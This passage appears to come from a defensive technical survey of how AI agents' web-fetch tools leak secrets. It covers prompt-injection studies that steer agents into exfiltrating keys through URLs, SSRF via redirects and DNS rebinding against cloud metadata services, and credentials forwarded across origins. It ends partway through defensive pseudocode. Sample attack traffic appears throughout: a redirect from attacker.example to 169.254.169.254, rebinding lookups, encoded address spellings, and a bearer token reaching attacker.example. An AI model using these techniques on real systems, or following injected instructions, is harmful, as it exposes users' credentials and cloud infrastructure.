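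The experiment varied where the instruction appeared on the page (four positions), whether the page loaded directly or after up to three redirects, and whether the model had to send the key whole or in four pieces. The researchers ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times, for 480 runs. They counted a success whenever a request reached their collecting server, so the result doesn't depend on interpreting the model's answers. In 120 further runs with harmless pages, the agent never contacted that server.

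It did so in 423 of the 480 attack runs, or 88.1%, slightly below the 89% given in the paper's abstract. In 95% of those 423 runs, the final answer looked harmless. The instruction's position on the page made little difference when the key was sent in one piece. Redirects made almost no difference, with rates of 88% for direct loading and 89% for redirect chains, so they don't help the attack when no filter is in place.

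Splitting the key was meant to deceive filters that look at one request at a time:

| Measure | Key sent whole | Key sent in four pieces |
|---|---|---|
| Runs with any request to the attacker's server | 99% | 77% |
| Leak@1 | 0.967 | 0.263 |
| Leak@3 | 0.967 | 0.158 |

The percentages in the top row are averages of the paper's results for each combination. They reflect a drawback for the attacker, which is that the small model often lost track of the longer instructions. The other two rows are harder to interpret. The paper defines Leak@*k* as the share of runs in which sensitive data, even a fragment, appears among the first *k* requests. Leak@3 therefore can't be lower than Leak@1, since the first three requests include the first one. The reported Leak@3 is lower, so the researchers must have measured something other than what they defined. They also define a completion rate, the share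 of runs in which all four pieces arrive, but don't report it, so we don't know how often the attacker gets the whole key. The fall in Leak@1 from 0.967 to 0.263 is still decent evidence that splitting hides a secret from simple filters.

Lan and colleagues also tested defences, with 30 runs each, against a page whose body contained an instruction to leak the whole key. A stern warning in the system prompt cut the leak rate from 100% to 66.7%. Tags that marked the page as untrusted data had no effect on their own, and combining them with the warning still left a leak rate of 56.7%. A list of permitted domains stopped every leak, as it was bound to, because the attacker's domain wasn't on it.

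Some of the other results are questionable. The "redirect detection" defence blocked everything, but it works largely by rejecting odd domain endings and paths with words such as "steal", which an attacker can avoid. The model made no attempts when a filter for random-looking strings was on. The paper suggests that the model avoids such strings when a filter is active, but a filter that inspects a finished URL shouldn't affect what the model tries to write unless something else in the set-up changed too.

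The study excludes all production models because the researchers feared breaking the providers' terms of service. They argue that larger models could be more vulnerable because such models follow instructions more reliably and use tools better. No one seems to have published a repeat of the experiment on a current frontier model, which would settle this directly.

### Asking the user first: Takedown

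One defence is to ask the user before each fetch. In *Takedown*, Lee, Kim and colleagues (2025) examined how eight widely used coding agents handle this by intercepting their traffic and reverse-engineering their code. Four had a built-in fetch tool, and three of those asked the user before fetching a page. The other, which the paper calls A4, did not.

A4's context normally includes the files the user has open. The agent could also read files anywhere on the computer without asking. Injected text could therefore make the agent read a private file and send its contents out in a URL with the fetch tool, without the user having a chance to object.

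An agent that asks for approval can still run some tools without asking. A1's own fetch tool always required approval, but A1 let third-party extensions set whether their tools required it. Of the ten most-installed extensions that offer tools in Microsoft's editor VS Code, seven didn't ask for approval, including a web search extension from Microsoft.

The agent A2 had no fetch tool but still leaked an API key. It could draw diagrams from Mermaid, a text notation that can include images from the web. Lee and colleagues put instructions in an issue, which is a public report on a software project. After reading the issue, A2 took the key from a file outside the project and drew a diagram with the key in an image's address. This was the image flaw of 2023, found two years later in a diagram feature, which people don't usually think of as a browser.

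The researchers could take arbitrary files from four of the eight agents without the user doing anything beyond normal work. In response to parts of the report, some vendors said the behaviour was intended, mostly on the grounds that the user starts the process by opening the hostile content. That is a weak excuse, because coding agents are meant to be used for opening web pages and cloning repositories.

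*Takedown* gives no success rates or model comparisons. It also omits the agents' names and versions because the vendors were still dealing with the reports, so readers can't check whether a particular product is still affected. It establishes whether an approval prompt exists, but not whether people use it well. Lan and colleagues doubt that they do, because users usually can't judge a request labelled as a connectivity check, and frequent prompts remove much of the benefit of using an agent.

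### Will better-trained models refuse?

None of these channels would matter if the model ignored the injected text. Developers have trained their models to do this, with some success by 2026. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reports that attacks on Claude Opus 5 failed in all 129 of Anthropic's browser scenarios. In a broader test by the security firm Gray Swan, the attack success rate after 15 attempts was 2.0%, down from 5.5% for Opus 4.8. Anthropic lists resistance to injection as the model's largest gain in agent safety.

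Google's newest models are at about the same level. Gray Swan launched a public tracker of such results late in 2026. iAfrica's *New Independent Tracker Finds Wide Safety Gaps Between AI Models* reports that, within 15 attacks, attackers compromised Gemini 4 Argon 2.3% of the time and Gemini 4 Carbon 2.5%, with Anthropic's models close behind.

In OpenAI's tests, GPT-5.6 Sol failed on about 0.05% of attacks typed straight into the chat, but on 3.77% of those in content that an agent processes (TechRepublic, *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks*, 2026). Pages retrieved by a web-fetch tool fall into the second category. The newer GPT-6 Sol scored 97.13% on defense against indirect injection (Cross, *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense*, 2026), which would leave about 2.9% of the attacks successful. OpenAI describes its flagship GPT-6 Astra as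 significantly more robust than GPT-5.6 Sol.

Failure rates were much higher a year earlier. The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* gives Opus 4.5 a failure rate of 4.7% for a single strong attack, 33.6% for ten and 63% for a hundred, and some rivals reached 92%. The tests probably differ too much for an exact comparison with Opus 5, but models have become more resistant, which counts against the prediction by Lan and colleagues that more capable models would be easier to hijack. Their figure of 0.89 would almost certainly be far lower on a current model from Anthropic, Google or OpenAI.

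But the improvement isn't universal. In the same Gray Swan tracker, attackers compromised Nvidia's Nemotron 3.5 Super VL 94.3% of the time. Fakti.bg's *Some AI Models Lie to Achieve Higher Scores* reports a rate of 64.7% for Moonshot's Kimi K3.1 Pro. Both companies publish models that anyone can download and run, and people who build their own agents often choose such models, so *Silent Egress* is still relevant to them.

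Gray Swan says it pays for its public evaluations itself and controls the findings, but it isn't fully independent of AI companies. It built 12 of the tracker's tests with Nvidia, and staff from OpenAI, Anthropic and Meta co-wrote its competition paper, *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026). Nvidia's bad result suggests that the partnership didn't earn it favorable treatment.

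A model's resistance to injection can vary widely with the setting. VentureBeat reports that Claude Opus 4.6 withstood all 200 injection attempts in a restricted coding environment. When the same model operated a graphical interface, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time, and by the 200th attempt the rate was 78.6%, or 57.1% with Anthropic's additional safeguards. Safeguards helped far more in another Anthropic test, on browser use, where they lowered the rate for Opus 4.5 from 8.0% to 1.4%. A score for one kind of agent is therefore poor evidence about another, and few scores existed in spring 2026. According to another VentureBeat article, Anthropic had published results for four settings, OpenAI for one and Google for none.

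A more basic problem is that a benchmark contains only the attacks its makers thought of. Anthropic commissioned a test of Claude Code's Auto Mode, a setting that replaces approval prompts with an automatic check. The testers ran 72 scenarios ten times each, and no attack succeeded. Heaton (2026) recounts in *The safety number that was zero until someone tried* that Rehberger then attacked the same mode, running Opus 5, and succeeded in roughly 60 to 80% of a small number of tries. His website never told the model to do anything harmful, but was arranged so that the agent's own reasonable steps led it to run his file. That attack ran code instead of leaking data through a URL, but it shows that training a model to refuse harmful instructions has a limit, because an attack may not contain any.

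More training data doesn't always help either. Zorz (2026), in *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection*, reports on research in which training on more injection attacks left agents easier to hijack, and suggests that a larger collection may just repeat the same attack. PromptArmor claims successful attacks on every provider's frontier models in *FrontierBreach*, a benchmark whose goals include data theft. PromptArmor sells AI risk assessments and benefits from this finding, but the claim is consistent with the small remaining attack success rates that the developers themselves publish.

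A model that usually refuses injected instructions makes theft rarer, but it doesn't make a URL safe to request. If a hostile page deceives only one agent in a thousand, and agents read it a hundred thousand times, the attacker still collects about a hundred people's data and loses almost nothing on the failed attempts.

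## From 2024: redirects that lead the tool into internal networks

The 2023 attacks used URLs to leak private data that the model had already read. A fetch tool can also reach data the model has never seen, on servers that accept no connections from the internet. From 2024, security researchers used AI products to reach such servers, even though the developers had blocked internal addresses. This usually worked because the product checked only the URL it received, then followed a redirect to an internal address.

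### Why internal servers answer

SSRF is older than AI agents. OWASP, a non-profit organisation that publishes a well-known list of web security risks, gave it its own category in 2021. According to OWASP's *A10:2021*, the flaw ranked first in a survey of the security community, although its average incidence in test data was only 2.72%. SecurityWeek's *Two New Web Application Risk Categories Added to OWASP Top 10* reports that the 2025 revision merged SSRF into Broken Access Control, which is reasonable because the attacker uses the server's access.

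A web-fetch tool routinely fetches untrusted URLs, whereas an ordinary web application does so in a few places, such as when a user imports a profile picture from a link. One standard precaution against SSRF is not to return raw responses to the requester, but a fetch tool can hardly follow it because its purpose is to return the content it fetches.

The most valuable target is usually the metadata service. Cloud providers run it to give programs tokens for the customer's storage and databases, since a password saved on the disk would be easy to steal. Its address, `169.254.169.254`, is link-local, meaning routers don't forward traffic to it, so only software on the machine can connect. But the service can't detect when that software is a fetch tool acting on a stranger's URL.

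*Server Side Request Forgery*, a course chapter from the University of Wisconsin, describes how an attacker used this route to breach the US bank Capital One. A misconfigured web firewall forwarded such a request, and the attacker used the credentials that came back to take over further resources.

Microsoft's cloud, Azure, requires requests to its metadata service to include the header `Metadata: true` and rejects any that contain `X-Forwarded-For`, a header that proxies add. These rules make redirect attacks harder because a server that issues a redirect chooses the next address but can't add headers to the next request. A simple fetch tool with a fixed set of headers would therefore get only an error. The rules offer much less protection if the attacker can also set the headers.

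### Copilot Studio, 2024

Many developers know about SSRF and refuse internal addresses. Their check typically works on the URL the tool receives:

```
GET /guide HTTP/1.1
Host: attacker.example

HTTP/1.1 302 Found
Location: http://169.254.169.254/
```

The tool looks up `attacker.example`, finds a public address and allows the request. The HTTP library then follows the redirect automatically, and no code checks the redirect's address against the list of forbidden addresses.

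The security firm Tenable found this gap in several Microsoft services. On 30 April 2024 it reported that Azure AI Studio and Azure ML Studio refused direct requests to internal hosts but followed 301 or 302 redirects to them. *SSRF Security Feature Bypass in Azure AI and ML Studios* (Tenable, 2024) describes a redirect to a monitoring page on the server itself, which could reveal the names of other internal machines. Microsoft had fixed the problem by 4 June. The same method worked on Azure Health Bot.

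It then worked on Copilot Studio, a product for building custom chatbots. A builder can set a chatbot to make an HTTP request when a user types a certain phrase. Tenable's *SSRFing the Web with the Help of Copilot Studio* lists what the researchers tried:

| Request | Result |
|---|---|
| the metadata address itself | blocked |
| the same address written as one decimal number | blocked |
| a host name that resolves to the address | blocked |
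| a public server that answers with a 301 to the address | got through, with an error from the metadata service |

Microsoft's check was quite good, since it resolved names and recognised an unusual spelling. It apparently ran only once per request.

The remaining error came from Azure's header rules, which require `Metadata: true` and forbid `X-Forwarded-For`. Copilot Studio let the builder add the first header but added the second automatically. It also had a second flaw: it accepted line breaks inside a header's value, so the researchers could push `X-Forwarded-For` into the request body, where the metadata service ignored it.

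The service then returned an access token, which the researchers used to list the resources available to the machine's identity. They found an internal database and the master keys for reading and writing it. The database accepted connections only from Microsoft's own infrastructure, so they sent the request through Copilot. They also reached other machines on the local network. Several customers shared this infrastructure. Tenable found no immediately accessible data belonging to other customers and didn't establish how much damage write access could have done. Microsoft classed the flaw, CVE-2024-38206, as critical.

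### Custom GPTs, November 2025

OpenAI had a similar problem a year later. Users can build a custom GPT, a version of ChatGPT for a particular purpose, and connect it to outside services through a feature called Actions. Jacob Krut, a security engineer at Open Security, was building one when he noticed that Actions sent requests to a URL he supplied.

The URL had to begin with `https`, but the metadata service uses plain `http`. That rule would have protected the service if OpenAI had applied it to redirects as well. Krut entered an `https` address on his own server, which redirected the request to the metadata service over `http`. To satisfy Azure's header rule, he used a setting that let him choose a header's name, and named the header `Metadata`.

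He obtained a token for the Azure identity behind the feature. According to SecurityWeek's *ChatGPT Vulnerability Exposed Underlying Cloud Infrastructure*, he could have used it to access ChatGPT's underlying cloud infrastructure. The article also reports that OpenAI rated the flaw high severity and quickly patched it. It doesn't describe the token's permissions, so it is hard to tell how far an attacker would have got.

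In both products, the attacker is a customer who configures the request. The attack doesn't rely on a hostile page or a deceived model, so better resistance to prompt injection would not have prevented it.

### DeepSeek TUI, May 2026

DeepSeek TUI is a terminal-based agent with a web-fetch tool called `fetch_url`. An attacker doesn't need an account, because they can supply the URL through prompt injection.

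The tool resolved the host name in the first URL and refused private, link-local and loopback addresses (those, such as `127.0.0.1`, that lead back to the machine itself). But the developer had configured the HTTP library to follow up to five redirects, and the tool didn't check where they went. Corgea's *DeepSeek TUI has SSRF via HTTP Redirect Bypass in fetch_url Tool* demonstrates this with two error messages. The tool reported a restricted address when it was given the metadata address directly, but a failed connection when a redirect led it there. The connection failed because the test machine wasn't in a cloud and had no metadata service, but the error proves that the tool had tried to connect.

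Corgea says an attacker could steal credentials this way on Amazon's, Google's and Microsoft's clouds. That seems too broad for Microsoft's, where the request must include the header `Metadata: true`, unless the attacker can also make the tool send that header. Other internal pages may not require a header.

The developer's notice of 9 May, *SSRF via HTTP Redirect Bypass in fetch_url Tool* (Hmbown, 2026), lists 0.8.22 as the fixed version. OSV's *GHSA-96ff-gc8g-wpvg* (2026) lists the flaw as CVE-2026-45310, with a severity of 7.4 out of 10.

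### PraisonAI's incomplete fix

The `web_crawl` tool in PraisonAI, a system for running teams of agents, went through several rounds of repair in 2026. GitLab's *CVE-2026-40150* (2026), dated 10 April, reports that the tool at first accepted any URL, including `file://` addresses, which name files on the machine's own disk. NVD's *CVE-2026-40160 Detail* describes the code that a fresh installation used by default, which followed redirects without validating any host.

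Version 1.5.128 added a check that looked up the host name in the URL and rejected loopback, private and link-local addresses. The tool then passed the URL to the HTTP library httpx with automatic redirects still switched on. The check did not cover redirects, although the report that prompted it had mentioned them. Rapid7's *CVE-2026-55523* calls this an incomplete fix and lists every version from 1.5.128 to 1.6.57 as vulnerable.

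Version 1.6.58 switched off automatic redirects. The tool now reads each `Location` header itself and checks the new host before it connects, according to SecureLayer7's *CVE-2026-55523*. A second record, CVE-2026-55525, seems to describe the same gap, since SecureLayer7's *CVE-2026-55525* attributes the fix to the same code change. The article also notes that a stolen secret can spread from the agent's context to logs and other tools.

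A test that requests `http://127.0.0.1` and expects a refusal would have passed on every vulnerable version of this check. To catch the flaw, a developer has to run a test server that redirects.

### One address, many spellings

Even without a redirect, a check can miss an internal address because someone has written it differently. An IPv4 address is a 32-bit number, and the usual form with dots is only a convenience. Each of the four parts is one byte, so the metadata address as a single number is:

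```
169 × 256³ + 254 × 256² + 169 × 256 + 254 = 2852039166
```

Many programs accept this number in a URL, and several other forms too:

| Spelling | Form |
|---|---|
| `169.254.169.254` | usual |
| `2852039166` | decimal |
| `0xa9.0xfe.0xa9.0xfe` | hexadecimal |
| `::ffff:169.254.169.254` | IPv4 address inside an IPv6 address |

A check that compares text stops only the spellings on its list. DeepSeek TUI needed another repair for a related reason. According to GitLab's *CVE-2026-45373* (2026), it blocked host names that resolved to a private IPv6 address but allowed the loopback address when it appeared directly in the URL, as in `http://[::1]`. The advisory refers to release 0.8.26.

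A model is no better than a text comparison at recognizing internal addresses. Mindgard's *TheLibrarian.io Internal Cloud Environment Access via web_fetch Tool* (2025) describes an AI assistant that refused to fetch `http://localhost` but accepted encoded variations of internal addresses. The refusal came from the model, and the client that fetched the pages evidently had no effective check.

The opposite mistake is to recognise IP addresses in every notation but never look up domain names. According to GitLab's *GHSA-vxgj-xg5c-p4h7* (2026), a guard shared by several of PraisonAI's other web tools had this flaw. Anyone could register a domain, point its DNS record to an internal address, and get past the guard.

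### DNS rebinding

A tool that checks a host name's address and then looks the name up again to connect is vulnerable to DNS rebinding, in which an attacker changes the address between the two lookups. The owner of a domain controls its DNS answers and sets how long other computers may store them, known as the TTL. If the TTL is zero, the second lookup goes back to the attacker's DNS server, which can give a different address.

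AutoGPT, a platform for building agents, had this flaw until version 0.6.1. Its code was more careful than DeepSeek TUI's or PraisonAI's. It looked up all the addresses of a host, rejected the URL if any was internal, and repeated the check at each redirect (though it also resent credential headers there). Then it passed the URL to the requests library, which looked up the name again. The report that led to the fix included two lookups of one test name, made in March 2025. With a placeholder for the name, they were:

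```
lookup 1   rebind.attacker.example   →   1.2.3.4
lookup 2   rebind.attacker.example   →   169.254.169.254
```

If the check gets the first answer and the library gets the second, the tool connects to the metadata service even though the check worked as intended. NVD's *CVE-2025-31490*, published in April 2025, concludes that an attacker could bypass all of AutoGPT's SSRF protection.

PraisonAI repeated the mistake a year later. *CVE-2026-55524* (2026), an entry by INCIBE, Spain's national cybersecurity institute, says that `web_crawl` was vulnerable to both redirects and rebinding until version 1.6.58. INCIBE's *CVE-2026-61430* (2026) says that rebinding still worked in versions before 1.6.78 because the tool didn't connect to the address it had checked. The second entry is probably right about rebinding, since SecureLayer7's description of the 1.6.58 patch mentions only a new check at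 each hop.

Rebinding fails over `https` because an internal server has no valid certificate for `rebind.attacker.example`. The attack therefore works mainly on services that use plain `http`, such as the metadata service. Requiring `https` at every hop blocks most of these attacks, but it also prevents the tool from fetching public pages that still lack encryption.

### The destination check

These failures suggest what a sound check has to do. The tool resolves the name, tests every address it gets, connects to an address it has tested, and does the same again at each hop:

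```python
def fetch(url):
    for _ in range(MAX_HOPS):
        scheme, host = parse(url)
        require(scheme in ("http", "https"))

        addresses = resolve_all(host)
        require(addresses and all(is_public(a) for a in addresses))

        reply = get(url, connect_to=addresses[0], follow_redirects=False)
        if not reply.is_redirect:
            return reply
        url = urljoin(url, reply.headers["Location"])

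    raise TooManyRedirects
```

A hostname can have several addresses, and the test has to cover all of them because a library may try another when the first doesn't respond. PraisonAI's check used the Python function `gethostbyname`, which returns only one IPv4 address, so it didn't test any others.

The `connect_to` setting prevents rebinding by making the library connect to the tested address without a second lookup. The `Host` header and the certificate check must still use the original name, or the connection will fail on almost any `https` site. Developers who run into this failure may be tempted to switch off certificate checks, which would let anyone on the network impersonate the site.

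The loop sends no credential headers. A tool that needs them also has to decide at each redirect whether the next host should receive them, because the destination check doesn't cover that.

### How Docker Agent does it

Docker Agent, the software company Docker's program for running AI agents, checks the address when it connects. Docker's *Fetch Tool* describes a tool that sends only GET requests and by default refuses to connect to non-public addresses. This is simpler than the loop above because the tool tests the address it is about to use, regardless of how the URL spelled it or what an earlier lookup returned. A redirect to a new host needs a new connection, so the tool checks that address too.

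The list of forbidden ranges needs some care too. The Model Context Protocol project publishes a list of its own in its security guidance:

| Range | What it leads to | Docker's list | MCP's list |
|---|---|---|---|
| `127.0.0.0/8`, `::1` | the machine itself | yes | yes |
| `10.0.0.0/8`, `172.16.0.0/12`, `192.168.0.0/16` | private IPv4 networks | yes | yes |
| `169.254.0.0/16`, `fe80::/10` | link-local addresses, including the metadata service | yes | yes |
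| `fc00::/7` | private IPv6 networks | not listed | yes |
| `0.0.0.0`, `::` | no particular address, but often the machine itself | yes | not listed |
| multicast | groups of machines | yes | not listed |

Docker's code may well block `fc00::/7` without the documentation listing it, but a company with an internal IPv6 network should test this.

Developers can also give the tool a list of permitted or forbidden hosts, which it applies to each redirect target too. The tool compares hosts with the list as text, and Docker warns that this comparison doesn't involve looking up names or recognising decimal or hexadecimal spellings of IP addresses. This does little harm as long as the connection check is on. But a developer whose agent has to read an internal wiki must switch the check off with the setting `allow_private_ips: true`. If the developer then forbids only `169.254.169.254`, an attacker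 can still reach the metadata service by writing the address as `2852039166`. A list of permitted hosts is much safer here, and Docker recommends one.

The design has another limit when requests go through a proxy, a server that sends them on the program's behalf. The program gives the proxy the host name and the proxy looks up the address, so a check inside the program can test only the proxy's own address. Docker Agent can send requests through a proxy in Docker Desktop, the company's application for developers' computers, and according to the documentation, the connection check doesn't cover those requests.

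For tools with the check, Docker limits this exception to hosts under its own domains, `docker.com` and `docker.io`. Before using the proxy, the agent looks up the hostname itself, and if any address it gets is private, the request stays on the checked path. If the lookup takes more than two seconds, the request can go to the proxy without an answer. To exploit this, an attacker would probably need some influence over the DNS records of Docker's domains.

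A tool's URL check can also fail when the tool hands the URL to a browser, because the browser then makes its own connections. PraisonAI could use Chromium to load pages, and INCIBE's *CVE-2026-61429* (2026) reports that the browser followed redirects and rebound DNS names to internal services after the tool's check had passed.

### What the guidance asks for

Published advice agrees that redirects are dangerous but differs on how to handle them. OWASP Cornucopia's *Server-Side Request Forgery (SSRF)*, which reproduces OWASP's recommendations, advises developers to disable redirects. It also advises them to use an allowlist of destinations and not to rely on a denylist, because attackers know how to bypass denylists.

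This is good advice for an application that calls three known services. A general web-fetch tool can't follow it fully, because its user may ask for any public page and many ordinary pages redirect to a new address. It has to block certain destinations and allow the rest. The fixes to DeepSeek TUI and PraisonAI support OWASP's distrust of blocklists, but in most of those cases the check examined the wrong thing, such as the first URL or the way an address was spelled. Blocking by IP address at connection time leaves far fewer ways to bypass the check.

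Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* fits fetch tools better. It says clients should apply the same checks to redirect targets as to the first URL, and consider following redirects manually so they can validate each hop. It also suggests connecting to the address that passed the check, and warns developers not to write their own code for parsing IP addresses. *Server Side Request Forgery (SSRF)*, in Mozilla's MDN reference for web developers, also advises against automatic redirects. The security firm Bishop Fox recommends checking the address after the DNS lookup and again after every hop.

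The MCP text's section on SSRF covers only the URLs that a client fetches while logging in to an MCP server, because a malicious server can fill these with internal addresses. Its only strict requirement is that clients running on a server consider the risk and take suitable measures, while its advice on redirects is a recommendation. A developer could follow the whole document and still publish a fetch tool that checks only the first URL. The draft submitted to the IETF in June 2026 addresses tools that take a URL and requires servers to treat every value in a tool call as untrusted, but it has no official standing.

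The MCP guidance also recommends that clients running on servers send all outgoing requests through an egress proxy that refuses internal destinations. Smokescreen is one such proxy. This solves the problem that Docker describes, because the check happens where the connection starts. It also covers requests from a browser or an overlooked library, provided that the network blocks all other outbound connections.

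Blocking private address ranges would not have covered everything in the Copilot Studio case. The database accepted requests because they came from Microsoft's infrastructure. A service at a public address can apply the same rule, and a destination check that looks only for private addresses would let requests to that service through. A machine identity with fewer permissions would have helped, because the researchers got into the database only after a machine that ran customers' chatbots was able to read the database's master keys.

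## From April 2025: credentials that follow a redirect to another origin

A tool that checks every redirect has to follow redirects itself instead of leaving them to its HTTP library. It then loses the library's protection, which removes at least some credential headers when a redirect leads to another host. AutoGPT's developers didn't replace that protection, and a flaw disclosed in April 2025 allowed a redirect to send the agent's keys to any public host. OpenClaw's developers added a replacement, but four advisories between March and June 2026 describe secrets that still reached the wrong origin.

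### How AutoGPT lost its library's protection

AutoGPT sends web requests through a wrapper, a layer of its own code around Python's requests library. The wrapper's purpose is to keep requests away from internal addresses. NVD's *CVE-2025-31491 Detail* describes how it handled redirects before version 0.6.1. One protection removed another in five steps:

1. Left to itself, the requests library follows redirects and drops the `Authorization` header when one leads to another host. It doesn't check whether the new address is internal.
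2. To add that check, AutoGPT's developers told the library not to follow redirects.
3. Their wrapper read the `Location` header, checked the new address and called the library again with the same headers.
4. The library treated this call as a first request. It had no previous host to compare with, so it removed nothing.
5. The new host received `Authorization`, `Proxy-Authorization` and any cookies the caller had set.

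With placeholder hosts, the result looked like this:

```
hop 1   GET https://api.example/redirect?url=https://attacker.example/
        Authorization: Bearer PLACEHOLDER-SECRET

hop 2   GET https://attacker.example/        (address check: public, allowed)
        Authorization: Bearer PLACEHOLDER-SECRET
```

The address check worked as intended on both hops. The wrapper followed redirects by default, so any part of AutoGPT that used it without changing that setting had the flaw.

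NVD's example is the code that reads data from GitHub, which sets an `Authorization` header with the user's GitHub credentials. The attacker would need an open redirect on GitHub's API and a way to make the agent visit it. NVD invented the redirect for its example. Its URL begins like the address of a normal comment and then goes back up the path with a series of `../` parts, so it would have passed a check on the beginning of the URL. OSV's *CVE-2025-31491* (2025) rates the flaw 8.6 out of 10. That is rather high for an attack on GitHub that depends on a hypothetical page, but reasonable for a wrapper that other parts of the program could use with other services.

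The security researcher Joshua Rogers came across the code after reading about an earlier SSRF flaw in AutoGPT. He recounts in *A small solution to DNS rebinding in Python* that he checked the code for DNS rebinding and found that it was vulnerable, and that it had "another issue", evidently the header leak. He reported the flaws to a platform that pays for such findings. Within hours, the platform wrongly marked his report as a duplicate and made it public, before AutoGPT had fixed the flaws. AutoGPT left the platform and fixed them with his help.

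Rogers's sample code for preventing rebinding doesn't follow redirects. He warns that anyone who adds redirect handling by hand has to keep cookies from leaking across origins, and suggests a cookie jar that ties each cookie to a domain. His code replaces the host name in the URL with the tested IP address, so he notes that cookies may have to be tied to that address instead. That would be risky because unrelated sites often share an address, so the jar could send one site's cookie to another.

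### OpenClaw's four leaks

OpenClaw has a shared function, `fetchWithSsrFGuard`, that guards against SSRF and follows redirects itself. From the start of this series of advisories, it removed some headers when a redirect led to another origin.

| Advisory | Published in 2026 | What reached the new origin | Fixed in |
|---|---|---|---|
| CVE-2026-32913 | 9 March | custom headers such as `X-Api-Key` | 2026.3.7 |
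| GHSA-68v4-hmwv-f43h | 3 April | `Authorization`, from the media downloader | 2026.3.31 |
| CVE-2026-40037 | 8 April | request bodies | 2026.4.8 |
| CVE-2026-53840 | 16 June | custom headers, from the MCP client | 2026.5.12 |

The guard originally removed four headers: `Authorization`, `Proxy-Authorization`, `Cookie` and the obsolete `Cookie2`. It forwarded every other header the caller had set, including `X-Api-Key` and `Private-Token`, according to OSV's *GHSA-6mgf-v5j7-45cr* (2026), which lists versions up to 2026.3.2 as affected and rates the flaw 9.3 (critical). The security firm Miggo, which analysed the patch, explains that the guard now keeps only headers on a list of safe ones, such as `Accept`, `Content-Type` and `User-Agent`. It will therefore remove new credential headers without an update.

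Three weeks later, OpenClaw fixed a leak of `Authorization` itself, the first header on every such list. OSV's *GHSA-68v4-hmwv-f43h* (2026) reports that the media downloader, a separate path for files, still forwarded the header in version 2026.3.28, which came out after the guard was fixed. The advisory doesn't explain the cause. In a similar earlier case, the Microsoft Teams plugin used its own fetch code for some attachments, so improving the guard's list would not have protected those downloads. OSV's *GHSA-7qf6-h84j-8fq4* describes a fix that sent them through the shared guard.

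The downloader's flaw scored only 6.0, although many more services use `Authorization` than `Private-Token`. The score is based on the assumption that an attack needs particular conditions and some action by the user, such as opening a file. That is a plausible reason for a lower rating, but a developer whose agent downloads files with a token should treat the two flaws as equally serious.

The third repair addressed request bodies, which a guarded request could resend after a redirect to another origin, as GitLab's *GHSA-qx8j-g322-qj6m* (2026) describes. A list of safe headers can't prevent this because it doesn't filter the body, just as header stripping doesn't protect a login form redirected with a 307. According to the entry, OpenClaw is a local assistant under its user's control, so the advisory doesn't assume a service shared by many customers. GitLab scores the attack 7.7 and classifies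 it as local. OSV's *CVE-2026-40037* (2026) gives it 7.1 and classifies it as a network attack, which fits better because the attacker is a remote server that answers with a redirect.

The last leak was in the client that connects OpenClaw to remote MCP servers. The operator who configures the agent can give each server custom headers, which often include an API key. If the server answered with a redirect to another origin, the client forwarded those headers there. According to Corgea's *MCP Streamable HTTP redirects could forward configured custom headers to another origin*, only the headers configured for that server were exposed. The attacker has to control the server or make it redirect, but doesn't need prompt injection. Corgea lists both 2026.5.8 and 2026.5.12 as safe versions but names 2026.5.12 as the first stable release with the fix. GitLab's *CVE-2026-53840* (2026) lists every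 version before 2026.5.12 as vulnerable. Corgea advises operators to replace any key that a redirecting server may have received.

None of these advisories on AutoGPT and OpenClaw reports an actual attack. Genevois Informatique's *CVE-2026-41345* (2026), which covers the media downloader, lists no entry in KEV, the US government's catalogue of flaws that attackers are known to have used, and estimates the chance of exploitation at below 1%. This is only mildly reassuring, because the owner of a leaked key would normally see nothing unusual. The redirected request appears in the attacker's log, and later use of the key looks like the agent's own.

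### Which headers should survive

AutoGPT resent every header when a redirect led to another origin. OpenClaw changed its rule for these redirects once, and Docker Agent uses yet another rule. A tool can remove named headers, keep only named headers, or remove headers according to who set them.

**Removing known credential headers** breaks the fewest programs, because harmless headers are kept after the redirect. Browsers remove only `Authorization`. Van Kesteren (2019) conceded, in a discussion of the plan to tie that header to the first origin, that developers who use other headers for credentials would be "out of luck". A longer list helps somewhat. According to SecureLayer7's *CVE-2026-55553*, versions of the JavaScript package urllib before 4.9.1 removed none of the six credential headers in a test, but the package now removes `x-api-key` among others. It will still miss a company's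 custom header, such as `X-Docs-Key`, and the developer gets no sign of this because the redirected request succeeds.

**Keeping only harmless headers** stops `X-Docs-Key`, but also stops any harmless header missing from the list of permitted ones. For example, a configuration in mcp-v8's *Configure Fetch Header Injection* sets `X-GitHub-Api-Version`, which tells GitHub which version of its interface the program expects. If the tool drops such a header when following a redirect to another origin, the server may answer in a different format without reporting an error. Private data can also get through if an operator puts it in a permitted header, such as an email address in `User-Agent`.

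**Removing every header the operator set** avoids both lists of names. Docker Agent's fetch tool lets an operator attach fixed headers to all its requests. Docker explains that Go's library already removes a few of them on a redirect to another domain, and that the tool removes the rest when the host changes, so the secret's name and position don't matter. However, this also removes the operator's harmless headers. These can replace the tool's usual `Accept` and `User-Agent`, so a site that returns data only to a particular client may refuse the request after a redirect.

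Docker's rule seems best for a web-fetch tool, which rarely needs any of the operator's settings to read a page on another site. The rule is harder to apply to a shared function like OpenClaw's, because many parts of the program call it and it may be unable to distinguish the operator's headers from others. Keeping only harmless headers is the better choice there.

Docker's documentation refers to a change of host, not of origin, so the tool might keep headers when only the port changes, or when a redirect goes from `https` to `http` on the same host.

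All three rules also apply only after the first request, which is too late if the first URL can be anything. Docker Agent attaches its fixed headers to every first request, even the one for `robots.txt`, the file that lists which pages automated visitors should avoid. Docker therefore tells operators to combine credentials with a list of permitted hosts. Binding the headers to one origin is stricter, because the tool then doesn't attach them to requests for any other origin.

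### The redirect procedure in full

The following pseudocode does this. The operator supplies the headers and `home`, the only `https` origin that may receive them. `origin()` returns the scheme, host and port, with the default port filled in.

```
 1  fetch(method, url, body, operator_headers, home):
 2      target  = parse(url)
 3      trusted = (origin(target) == home)
 4
 5      for hop in 1 to 6:
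 6          require target.scheme in (http, https)
 7          require target has no user name or password
 8          require site_allowed(target.host)
 9          address = resolve_and_check(target.host)
10
11          headers = tool_defaults()
12          if trusted: headers.update(operator_headers)
13          log(hop, origin(target), names(headers))
14          reply = send(method, target, headers, body,
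15                       connect_to=address, follow_redirects=off)
16          if not reply.is_redirect: return reply
17
18          next = parse(reply.location, relative_to=target)
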